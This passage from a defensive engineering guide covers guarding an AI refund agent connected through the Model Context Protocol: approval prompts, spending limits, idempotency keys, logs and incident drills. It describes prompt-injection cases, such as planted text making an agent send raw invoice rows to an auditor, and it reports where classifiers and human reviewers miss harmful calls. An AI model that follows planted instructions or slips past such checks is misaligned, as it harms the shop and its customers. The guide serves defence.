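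A daily limit also resets every day, so a fault that began just before midnight could cost $10,000 within minutes, and one that nobody noticed for 16 days could cost the full $80,000. An attacker who used up the day's total early would make honest customers wait for a person or for the next morning. The shop also has no limit per customer, so someone with ten $55 orders could claim that everything had arrived broken and collect $550.

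The customer with the broken lamp might also have bought a $45 rug that arrived in good condition. If the model confused the two orders and refunded the rug, the shop would lose $45. The gateway would allow the call because the customer would be the right one, the amount would be permitted, there would be no earlier refund, and the day's total would stay within its limit.

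## Decide which calls a person must approve

The shop's gateway can check that order 5090 belongs to the customer and that $310 is no more than the customer paid. It can't detect that the customer complained about the lamp and was happy with the desk, but a member of staff who reads the ticket can. An approver can judge whether a call serves its purpose, even in cases nobody foresaw when writing the rules. This takes time and attention, so the shop asks for approval only when the gateway holds a call.

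### When hosts ask

The Model Context Protocol recommends that clients ask for confirmation before sensitive operations and show the user a tool's inputs before sending them to the server, so the user can stop private data from leaking. But a host that never asks for confirmation can still use the protocol correctly, so the developer has to check what each host does.

By default, OpenAI's service sends an `mcp_approval_request` before every MCP call. The developer's program answers with an `mcp_approval_response`, which covers only that call. The developer can list tools that skip approval, or set `require_approval` to `never` for the whole server. If the shop connected its help desk this way, it could exempt `get_ticket` and keep approval for `reply_to_ticket`. OpenAI advises developers to always require approval for sensitive actions, but its service can't detect whether a person saw the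 request, so it also accepts approvals from a program that answers yes every time.

Claude Code, by contrast, now asks for approval less often. It used to ask the user before running commands or changing files. According to Anthropic's *Auto mode is now the default in Claude Code* (2026), new sessions on the Pro, Max and Team plans have started in *auto mode* since 14 August, unless the user or an administrator had chosen another default. In this mode, a second model called a *classifier* sorts actions into safe and dangerous, and its decision replaces the user's. If it blocks a call, the agent looks for another way. After three blocks in a row or twenty in a session, Claude Code goes back to asking the user, or stops if there is no user to ask, as Anthropic's *How we built Claude Code auto mode* explains.

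A developer who moves an agent from one host to the other may therefore lose prompts that they were relying on.

### Confirmations that a server requests

An MCP server can also ask for confirmation in the middle of a call. Suppose the payment company's server wants a person to confirm refunds above $200. Model Context Protocol's *Multi Round-Trip Requests* (2026) sets out the exchange:

1. The client calls `refund_order` for $310.
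2. The server replies with a result marked `input_required`. It contains a question for the user and may contain `requestState`, a block of data that only the server can interpret.
3. The client shows the question and collects the answer.
4. The client repeats the call with a new `id`, the answer and the unchanged `requestState`.
5. The server checks what it received and makes the refund.

Model Context Protocol's *2026 07 28 release candidate* (2026) lets a server send the user a question only while it is handling a client's request, so every question should relate to something the user or their agent started. The user can accept, decline or dismiss the question. Model Context Protocol's *Elicitation* (2026) requires the client to show which server sent the question. If the server needs a password or payment details, it must send the user to a web page, and the client must show the page's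 full address before opening it.

In Model Context Protocol's release post, the database company Supabase welcomed the new method because its tools could use it to ask users to confirm the cost of a new project or a query that would delete data. Both the client and the server have to support the method. Developers using the official TypeScript SDK have to turn on the July version, according to Model Context Protocol's *Supporting protocol revision 2026-07-28*.

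These questions help when the server's operator is honest and the agent has made a mistake, but they don't protect anyone from a hostile server, because its operator writes them. The server could show "Refund $40 for the lamp?" and pay out $310, or show no question. It also receives the call's arguments before the question appears, so if they include a customer's address, declining doesn't take it back. The shop's gateway therefore has to show its own question before it sends the call.

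An honest server can't verify who answered, either, since a carelessly built host could accept on the user's behalf. A payment company that needs certainty can send the user to its own web page and check their login there.

### What the approver has to see

*Don't Let AI Agents YOLO Your Files* (2026) analyses 290 incident reports about agents and files, and finds that user review contributed to 105 of the incidents. In 80, the user had approved actions automatically. In 31, the prompt showed a command but not its effect on the files. For example, a prompt for `python3 setup.py` looks routine, but approving it allows any code in the file to run.

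For the refund of the desk, the shop's gateway shows this page:

```text
REFUND REQUEST                 opened 10:42, expires 10:52

Pay       $310.00 to the card ending 4421, which paid for order 5090
Through   refund_order, api.payments.example
Order     5090: one desk, delivered, $310.00 paid, no earlier refund
Customer  "The lamp in order 5127 arrived broken.
writes    The desk from order 5090 is lovely."
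Undo      Not possible once the refund has completed

          [ Refuse ]     [ Refund $310.00 ]
```

The gateway takes the amount and order number from the call, and the rest from the shop's configuration, the order database, the payment company and the help desk. The page labels the customer's words as the customer's, because a dishonest customer could write "your manager has already agreed to this". The page includes the line about undoing the refund because *Let the Agent Do It?* (2026), a study of how software practitioners make permission decisions, suggests that prompts should show whether an action is recoverable.

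The arguments are the only text on the page that the model wrote. If the page also showed the model's summary of the call, a model that had confused the desk with the lamp would probably write "refund for the broken item", which fits the complaint. Planted text that caused the call could shape the summary too. Anthropic removes the agent's explanations before its classifier judges a call, so that they can't lead the classifier to a bad decision. When Anthropic left in those explanations and the tools' results, the classifier did worse on Anthropic's test of actions that went beyond the user's request.

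Even a call's exact arguments may not give the reviewer enough information. *When a Permitted Action Completes a Forbidden Workflow* (Hossain, Shayoni and colleagues, 2026) describes a user who asks an agent to send an auditor summary totals only. Planted text makes the agent copy raw invoice rows into `report.csv`, and the agent then asks to send that file to the auditor. The tool, the recipient and the file name all look right, so the reviewer can recognise the problem only by knowing how the agent made the file.

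They tested four kinds of prompt on 80 volunteers, who each judged six harmful and six legitimate requests:

| What the prompt showed | Harmful requests approved | Legitimate requests approved | Median time per decision |
|---|---|---|---|
| Short description of the action | 55.0% | 91.7% | 16.3 s |
| Exact arguments as well | 43.3% | 90.0% | 23.4 s |
| Also the user's original limits and a log of earlier steps | 32.5% | 87.5% | 38.6 s |
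| The same facts, with the relevant steps linked and their combined effect stated | 24.2% | 85.8% | 33.2 s |

Most of the improvement came from giving people more facts. The last design's advantage over the plain log could be due to chance, since only 20 people used each version. The statements of combined effect were also correct throughout the study, but in practice software has to produce them, and Hossain and colleagues' monitor detected 89.2% of violations in a separate test. They warn that a confident but wrong statement could mislead reviewers, but they haven't tested this yet.

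### Approve one exact call, for a short time

Approving a $40 refund doesn't help if the agent can then send $310. The gateway prevents this by storing the held call and sending the stored copy once a staff member approves it, so the model can't change it. If the model has to repeat the call, the gateway can save a hash of the server, tool and arguments with the approval and refuse any call that doesn't match. If an argument names a file, the hash should also cover the file's contents, because the agent could replace the file after the approval.

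The facts behind an approval can also change. While the page for the desk is open, a colleague might refund the same order by hand. The shop therefore lets each page expire after ten minutes, accepts each approval only once, and rechecks the order and amount just before sending the call.

The Model Context Protocol includes similar advice for servers that use `requestState`. The server should tie the state to one user, make it expire soon and include a digest of the call's main arguments. A client can still use the same state twice before it expires, so a server that makes payments has to record which states it has already accepted.

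Many people grant much broader approvals. Anthropic reports that by June 2026, 49.5% of active users of Claude Code's command-line version had written a standing rule that allows some shell commands. Many of these rules covered a whole programming language, as `python:*` does, which in practice allows any program to run. Auto mode does not apply these broad rules.

A refusal needs to cover more calls than an approval does. One person interviewed for *Let the Agent Do It?* had refused several requests, but the agent carried on by another route. At the shop, a refused refund blocks all further refunds from that ticket until a staff member reopens the ticket.

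### How carefully people approve

Users approve 97% of Claude Code's permission prompts, according to Anthropic, but most of those prompts probably concern harmless commands. To test whether people catch dangerous ones, Anthropic hired 1,053 professional testers through a research company for what they knew only as a coding study. Partway through each session, the researchers replaced the text of one prompt with a clearly dangerous command, and 143 testers (13.6%) refused it. The refusal rate fell from about 17% early in a session to about 5% after 50 or more prompts. Claude Code's auto mode blocked 937 (89%) of the same commands.

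The testers worked in a test environment with nothing of their own to lose, and Anthropic published the results to justify its new default. People guarding their own money might do better. But low stakes don't easily explain the decline within a session, because the stakes were just as low at the start.

Reviewers were more careful in *Do User-Authored Permission Policies Improve Protection Against AI Agent Overreach?* (Yan, 2026). The 113 participants, none from the software industry, supervised a simulated agent through 18 actions, seven of which went beyond the assigned task. Those who reviewed each action individually blocked 59.6% of the seven. They saw only 18 prompts and had reason to refuse 39% of them, so they had little chance to form a habit of approving.

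People may also have approved some of Yan's seven actions because they wanted them, rather than out of carelessness. Of the people asked about every action, 88% let the agent call the airport to confirm a flight, although nobody had requested the call.

### Would fewer prompts get more attention?

The case for asking rarely is that people tire of prompts and stop reading them. The drop from 17% to 5% supports this, as does another Anthropic finding, that users reject 39% of Claude Code's plans but 3% of its permission requests. But users may reject a plan because they prefer a different solution, so the comparison doesn't measure how well they spot danger.

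People also seem less likely to approve calls one by one as they gain experience. Resilient Cyber's *the human in the loop illusion* reports, from an earlier Anthropic study, that new users approve everything automatically about 20% of the time, and users with 750 sessions more than 40%. Experienced users also interrupt the agent more often, according to Digital Watch's *AI agent autonomy rises as users gain trust in Anthropic’s Claude Code*. Watching and interrupting can work for an hour of coding, but a refund goes through before anyone can react.

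Yan's study is the main evidence against relying on fewer prompts. A second group set rules in advance for spending, sending, deleting and reading private data, which cut the prompts from 18 to about 11. They blocked only 40% of the unrequested actions. When a prompt did ask them about an unrequested action, they approved it 67% of the time, compared with 40% in the group that saw every prompt. They didn't reliably save time either, once Yan counted the time spent setting the rules.

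The number of prompts fell only from 18 to 11, and participants had chosen "ask" for 81% of their rules, so the prompts still mixed harmless actions with doubtful ones. The study doesn't test prompts that appear only when something is unusual, but it casts doubt on the assumption that people who see fewer prompts automatically review each one more carefully. Rarer prompts could even make reviews worse if reviewers come to expect that every request is fine. An organization that asks less often also has to give its reviewers better information and check that they use it.

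### What an automated approver misses

A classifier doesn't get tired as a human reviewer does, but it still makes errors. In Anthropic's tests, the auto mode classifier wrongly blocked 0.4% of 10,000 real tool calls. It missed 5.7% of 1,000 artificial attempts to send data out, and 17% of 52 real cases in which an agent had done more than the user authorised. In most of the misses that Anthropic examined, the classifier identified the action as dangerous but wrongly treated it as having the user's consent. A user who said "clean up the PR", for instance, hadn't agreed to overwrite the project's history.

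Anthropic also commissioned Trajectory Labs to run tests with planted instructions. None of the attacks succeeded against three Claude models in auto mode. But even with the permission checks switched off, attacks on Anthropic's latest models succeeded only 0.09% of the time on average, so the classifier can have added very little protection in that test. Anthropic still recommends that people review the agent's actions when it makes high-stakes changes to live systems.

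The design would also be a poor fit for the shop, because Anthropic's classifier treats the user's messages as the authority on what the agent may do, and the shop's users are strangers who want refunds. A classifier could still be useful there if it could only add calls to the queue for staff and never release any.

### The shop's approval queue

At 33 seconds per decision, the median for the best prompt in Hossain and colleagues' study, staff would spend about 11 minutes a day on the 20 refunds over $60, plus the time for any held replies. Approving all 150 refunds would take 83 minutes. Each refund also involves at least reading a ticket and sending a reply, so approving every call would take more than four hours, and staff would pass their fiftieth prompt early in the day.

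Refunds that staff approve don't count towards the $5,000 daily limit, so an agent stuck in a loop, or an attacker with many tickets, could fill the queue until someone starts approving requests without checking them. The gateway therefore forwards at most 40 refund requests a day. It holds any others and alerts the head of customer service.

The head of customer service also sends staff one false request a week, such as the refund for the undamaged desk, to help the shop tell whether they are still reading the requests. If someone approves it, the gateway discards it. Even if staff approve every real request for months, that wouldn't justify raising the $60 limit, because, as *Let the Agent Do It?* points out, repeated approval can come from fatigue or pressure to keep work moving.

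## Test the limits, prevent repeated actions and prepare to undo them

The shop's gateway should hold a $310 refund, and its proxy should block requests to strangers' servers. A mistake in either could go unnoticed for months, because a well-behaved agent rarely reaches the limits. The developer tests the gateway and the proxy without a model, since a model asked to break a rule may decline and leave the rule untested.

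### Call the gateway and the proxy directly

One script sends tool calls to the gateway in the host's format. Another runs inside the sandbox and makes the web requests that a broken tool might make. Both run on a copy of the shop's set-up with test accounts, so a failed test does no harm.

| Test | Expected result | Log entry that proves it |
|---|---|---|
| Call `message_all_customers` | The gateway refuses | Gateway: "tool not on list". The help desk's test server has no record of the call |
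| Request `stats.stranger.example` through the proxy | The proxy refuses | Proxy: the host name and "host not on list" |
| Send the same request around the proxy | The connection fails | Firewall: a blocked connection from the sandbox |
| Follow a redirect from the staff chat to `files.stranger.example` | The proxy allows the original request and refuses the redirect | Proxy: an allowed entry for the chat, then a refusal for the new host |
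| Refund $60.01 from a $90 order | The gateway holds the call | Gateway: "over $60". The payment test account shows no refund |
| With $4,970 already refunded, request $25 and $30 at the same moment | The gateway allows one and holds the other | Gateway: one "allowed", one "daily total reached", and a total of $4,995 or $5,000 |
| Add a word to the description of `reply_to_ticket`, then call it | The gateway refuses | Gateway: "definition changed", with the old and new hashes |
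| Approve a held refund after eleven minutes | The gateway sends nothing | Gateway: "approval expired", with the approver's name and the time |

An error message doesn't prove that the gateway refused the call, because the server can return one too. The help desk's server would refuse `message_all_customers` because the agent's token lacks the scope. Model Context Protocol also defines an error, -32602, that a server returns when a client calls a tool the server doesn't have. The developer therefore checks that the gateway's log shows the rule refusing the call and that the receiving system got no call.

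A gateway that refused everything would pass most of these tests, so the script also sends calls that should succeed, such as a refund of exactly $60. The measurement needs a check too. *Deploying MCP 2026-07-28 servers on AWS* (Akuma, 2026) describes a script that runs a cloud function directly, sends three requests with missing or false credentials through the gateway, and runs the function directly again. It finds each refusal in the gateway's log by its request number, then waits until the cloud provider's count of function runs settles at exactly two. The direct runs show that the counter works, so a total of two means none of the bad requests reached the function.

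Two simultaneous refunds are harder to test, because one usually finishes before the other starts. Akuma's tests force the overlap by making both calls read the same starting value before either can write, then check that only one succeeds. These tests use a stand-in for the database, so they check the code's logic but not the real database's behaviour. The shop should also repeat its own test several hundred times on the database software it uses in production. The other tests need only one run after each change to a rule, tool or software library, because fixed rules give the same answer every time.

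### Run the whole agent in a test account

To measure how often the agent stays within the limits but refunds the wrong item, which direct tests can't show, the developer runs the complete agent on invented tickets and on old ones with the personal details removed. Some of the tickets come from customers with several orders, and some contain planted instructions. After each run, a script compares the refunds, notes and replies in the test accounts with a list of what should have changed. The agent's own report isn't good evidence, because in earlier research agents often finished the user's task while also carrying out an attack.

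Suppose the agent makes no wrong refund in 300 runs. That doesn't show that its error rate is zero. If the agent errs in a fraction *p* of runs, and the runs are independent, the chance of 300 clean runs is (1 − *p*) multiplied by itself 300 times. The developer can find the rate at which a clean result would have only a 5% chance:

```text
(1 - p)^300 = 0.05
p = 1 - 0.05^(1/300) = 0.0099, or about 1%
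```

If the rate were above 1%, the test would produce a clean result less than 5% of the time, so a clean result is good evidence that the rate is below 1%. Three divided by the number of clean runs gives this upper limit approximately.

| Clean runs | Error rate still possible, at 95% confidence | Wrong refunds at 150 refunds a day |
|---|---|---|
| 30 | Up to 9.5% | Up to 14 a day |
| 300 | Up to 1.0% | Up to 1.5 a day |
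| 3,000 | Up to 0.1% | Up to about one a week |

An agent that errs once in 500 refunds, or about twice a week at this shop, would pass a 300-run test 55% of the time. The developer would need about 1,500 runs to have a 95% chance of seeing the error. If one of the 300 test refunds goes wrong, the upper limit on the error rate rises to about 1.6%. The developer can fix the cause and start the test again, but shouldn't keep repeating the batch until one has no errors.

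The calculation also assumes that the test tickets are a fair sample of future ones. Running the same ticket 300 times reveals little about any other, and a new version of the model needs a new test. The figures don't apply to a thief, who can keep rewriting a ticket until one version works. Against a thief, the shop has to rely on the limits it tested directly.

### When the reply gets lost

Suppose order 5127 also included a $50 mirror, so the customer paid $90. The refund tool requests $40 for the broken lamp. The payment company pays, but the connection breaks before its reply arrives. The tool can't distinguish this from a request that never reached the company. If it sends the refund again, the customer gets $80. The payment company has no reason to reject the second refund because the total is still below $90.

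The gateway would hold another refund request from the model, because the order already has an automatic refund. But some HTTP libraries repeat failed requests on their own after the gateway has made its decision. Slides by Munjal for the MCP Dev Summit describe a timeout as an unknown outcome rather than a failure, and list five layers that may each retry independently. If each layer made up to three attempts, one call could become 243 requests.

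The July 2026 Model Context Protocol specification requires clients to resend a lost call as a new request, with no exception for tools that move money. A host that automatically resends every lost call could therefore follow the specification and pay twice. It is safer to read the rule as describing how to resend a call, and to let the host resend a payment only if the receiving system can recognise it as a repeat.

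The broken connection doesn't reliably stop the original call either. The Model Context Protocol requires the server to treat a closed stream as a cancellation, but only recommends that it stop work as soon as practical. The protocol also bars the server from sending further messages about the request, so a server that has already paid the $40 can comply without reporting the payment.

The proposal that removed resumable connections from Model Context Protocol says that work must use *tasks*, an optional extension, if it has to survive a dropped connection. The server returns an identifier for the work, and the client uses it to ask for the result later. If the connection breaks before the client receives the identifier, the client doesn't know whether the work began. It also can't list tasks to find out, because the redesigned extension no longer has a command for that.

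### One $40 refund with an idempotency key

An *idempotency key* is an identifier sent with a request so that the receiving system carries out a repeated request only once. If the shop's payment company handles keys as Stripe's *Idempotent requests* describes, the refund works like this:

1. Before contacting the company, the refund tool's code creates a random key and saves it with the order number and the amount.
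2. The code sends the refund with the key in a header:

```http
POST /v1/refunds HTTP/1.1
Host: api.payments.example
Idempotency-Key: 8f1c27ab-5d0e-4c9b-9a63-1b7e40d2f6c8

{ "order": "5127", "amount_usd": 40 }
```

3. The company finds no earlier request with this key, so it refunds $40 and saves its reply under the key.
4. The connection breaks before the reply arrives.
5. The code sends the saved request again with the same key.
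6. The company finds the key, checks that the details match, and returns the saved reply without moving any money.
7. The code reports one successful refund to the model.

The code saves the key before sending anything so it can still find the key if the host crashes and restarts. It uses a new key for each refund instead of the order number because the customer may later need a separate refund for the mirror.

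The model shouldn't create the key. tianpan.co's *Exactly-Once Was Hard Before Your Agent Could Retry Itself* (2026) explains that after a timeout, the model writes a new call, perhaps with a reworded argument or an extra field, instead of the agent replaying its saved request. If the key were a hash of the request, the new wording would produce a new key and the company would pay again. tianpan.co's *The Idempotency Key Your Agent Forgot to Send* (2026) recommends putting the key in the ordinary code between the model's decision and the outside effect, since that code runs the same way every time. The shop's refund tool therefore repeats the saved request itself. If it still gets no answer, it reports to the model that the result is unknown and flags the refund for staff to check.

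The code also has to know when to stop. Stripe's *Advanced error handling* gives these rules for version 1 of its API:

| What the code receives | What it means | What to do |
|---|---|---|
| No reply | The refund may or may not have happened | Repeat it with the same key and details, within 24 hours of the original request |
| Status 409 | An earlier attempt with this key may still be running | Wait, then repeat with the same key |
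| Status 500 | The outcome is unknown, and the same key returns the same saved error | Look up the refund before trying anything else |
| Still no result after 24 hours | Stripe may have deleted the key, so a repeat could count as a new refund | Stop repeating and check the account |

Creating a new key is a mistake in all four cases, because it can start a second refund. If the shop can't establish what happened, Stripe advises contacting support before repeating the operation. Other companies keep keys for different periods. Chargebee's *Idempotent requests* gives a window of 30 minutes, so a program that retries failed requests hourly would be safe with Stripe for a day but could repeat an action at Chargebee on its first retry.

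Some tools have no key to send. If the help desk's server doesn't support one and the response to a `reply_to_ticket` call gets lost, the host should read the ticket to see whether the customer already has the message. The host can't check the staff chat this way, because the shop's webhook can post messages but can't read them. If the response to a post gets lost, the tool should report that the note may have been posted instead of posting it again, since the warehouse's automation could act on both copies.

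### Don't rely on a server's claim that a call is safe to repeat

The `idempotentHint` that Model Context Protocol (2026) describes omits information a client needs, even when the server's developer sets it in good faith. It covers only repeated calls with the same arguments, and the model may change them. It has no time limit, but the payment company behind the server may delete its idempotency keys after a day. The developer may also have overlooked an effect, such as an email that goes out on every call. If the server is untrusted, the hint may be deliberately false.

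The developer should check the documentation for an idempotency key and how long it works, then test both. In the test account, the developer sends a refund, cuts the connection before the reply, repeats the call with the same key and checks that only one refund was made. Repeating the key with a different amount should produce an error.

If the shop ran its own MCP server, the server would need to record completed calls. In Akuma's design, the server saves the change and its reply in a single database transaction, so a crash can't leave the change in place without a record of it. A refund at another company can't be part of that transaction, so the server has to save a key first and then pass it to the payment company.

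### Record each call and its result

The gateway writes a log entry before it sends a call and adds the result afterwards. An entry without a result therefore identifies a call whose outcome somebody has to check. For the lamp, the completed entry is:

```json
{
  "time": "2026-10-07T10:52:14Z",
  "trace": "4bf92f3577b34da6a3ce929d0e0e4736",
  "ticket": "88214",
  "tool": "refund_order",
  "arguments": { "order": "5127", "amount_usd": 40 },
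  "destination": "api.payments.example:443",
  "rule": "refund up to $60, policy version 12",
  "decision": "allowed",
  "approver": null,
  "result": "refunded",
  "attempts": 2,
  "replayed": true
}
```

The last two fields show that the tool sent the refund request twice and received the saved reply the second time. The gateway uses the same format to log calls it refuses or holds, because a series of refusals may be the first sign of an attack. The agent's credentials shouldn't let it edit or delete the log.

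Logging every argument in full would create another store of private data. Akuma's server leaves access tokens, arguments and returned data out of its log and records a hash of the operation instead. That suits an operator who mainly needs to match repeated calls. The shop has to reconstruct payments, so it logs order numbers and amounts. For a reply to a customer, it logs only a hash and the number of the ticket that contains the text.

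If OpenAI's service calls an MCP server directly, the shop's gateway can't log the call, but the developer can save the `mcp_call` items that OpenAI returns. These contain the arguments, the server's output and any error.

### Follow one call across several systems

One refund leaves records in the host, the gateway, the proxy and the payment company. A *trace identifier* links them. The July specification documents a standard place for it in an MCP request:

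```json
"_meta": {
  "traceparent": "00-4bf92f3577b34da6a3ce929d0e0e4736-00f067aa0ba902b7-01"
}
```

The long number identifies the whole chain of calls, and the shorter one after it identifies the step that sent this request. Each system keeps the long number and adds a number for its own step. According to Körbächer, a developer can then follow a call from the host through the gateway and the MCP server to the services behind it. If a reply is lost and the host repeats the MCP request, the second attempt has a new request ID, but both attempts appear together if the host keeps the same trace identifier.

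This works only where every system passes the identifier on and lets the developer read its records. The help-desk company may do neither. The shop can see what it sent to the server, what came back and how long the call took, but not which other companies received the ticket, whether the server kept a copy, or whether a reported success is true. A trace from an honest server operator might show some of this, but a hostile operator could leave out any step.

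To check what a server reports, the shop needs a record that the server doesn't control. Every night, a script compares the gateway's log with the payment company's list of refunds. A refund that appears only in the company's list may mean someone has stolen the key or found a way around the gateway, while one that appears only in the gateway's log may mean a customer is still waiting for money. Akuma similarly uses the cloud provider's records of database access to look for access by anything other than the server, but notes that these records arrive too late to serve as an alarm.

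### Add delays and keep separate backups

Before an incident, the developer has to find out which actions the shop can reverse and how quickly it must do so. After the PocketOS loss, Railway extended its 48-hour delay to deletions made through the API, and Abdelwahab writes that Railway now delays deleting the backups too. The delay protects customers whether the call came from a model's mistake, a thief or a typing error, because Railway doesn't have to recognise the cause.

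The delay helps only if somebody notices in time, so the shop needs an alert for every scheduled deletion. The delay also may not cover every destructive command. In May, it didn't cover wiping a volume at Railway. A customer should delete a test volume through the API and restore it, then wipe the volume and try to restore it again.

The shop also copies its order database every night to an account at another company. The hosting key can't reach that account, and the key that uploads the copies can't delete them. The shop could still lose up to a day of orders. Once a month, the developer restores a copy to a test machine to check that it's readable, because an unreadable backup is hard to spot without trying to use it.

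Refunds are much harder to reverse. Stripe's *Canceling a refund* says that a refund can be cancelled only for a very short time after it is sent. If a card refund can still be cancelled, a person has to do it in Stripe's dashboard. Stripe's *Cancel a refund* shows that the API can cancel only refunds that are waiting for the customer to act, a state that most card refunds never enter. According to Stripe's *Refund and cancel payments*, the money can appear on a customer's bank statement in real time, depending on the card network and the bank.

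The shop therefore adds its own delay by holding each automatic refund in a queue for an hour before sending it. Even if all 130 of a normal day's automatic refunds arrived within eight hours, about 16 would be waiting at a time. If more than 40 are waiting, the gateway pauses the queue and alerts staff. An agent stuck in a fast loop would trigger this pause before any of its refunds went out. Refunds from a slower fault could still go out, up to the daily limit of $5,000.

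### Stop the agent before replacing its keys

In an emergency, replacing the payment key may seem like the obvious first step. But the queued refunds would fail only until the developer installed the new key, and then the shop would send them. The developer should work in this order:

1. Set the gateway to refuse every call and pause the refund queue. Each queued job checks this setting just before it sends anything.
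2. Stop work that other systems have already accepted, such as scheduled messages at the help desk or parcels that the warehouse's automation has put on hold. Their owners may have to do this.
3. Cancel the agent's credentials and create new ones.
4. Use the logs and the other companies' records to list what happened, then undo the effects with the nearest deadlines first.

A tool call can keep running after the client disconnects, which is partly why Akuma's server limits each call to 60 seconds.

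Cancelling access may also cover less than the developer expects. Stripe's *Model Context Protocol (MCP)* explains that an administrator can revoke a client's session, but only for the account or organisation and the environment that the administrator is viewing. The session stays active elsewhere, so someone with several accounts has to check each one. An unrevoked session expires 14 days after the user authorised it, which is far too long to wait in an emergency. After cancelling a credential, the developer should try a harmless lookup with it to confirm that the server refuses. Some servers save the results of token checks, so if the lookup still works, the developer should repeat it a few minutes later.

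The shop practises these steps twice a year in its test accounts. The developer queues 50 refunds, starts the agent on a batch of tickets, and asks a colleague who didn't build the system to stop everything by following only the written instructions. The test passes if no queued refund goes out, the old keys stop working, and the colleague can list every change the agent made.
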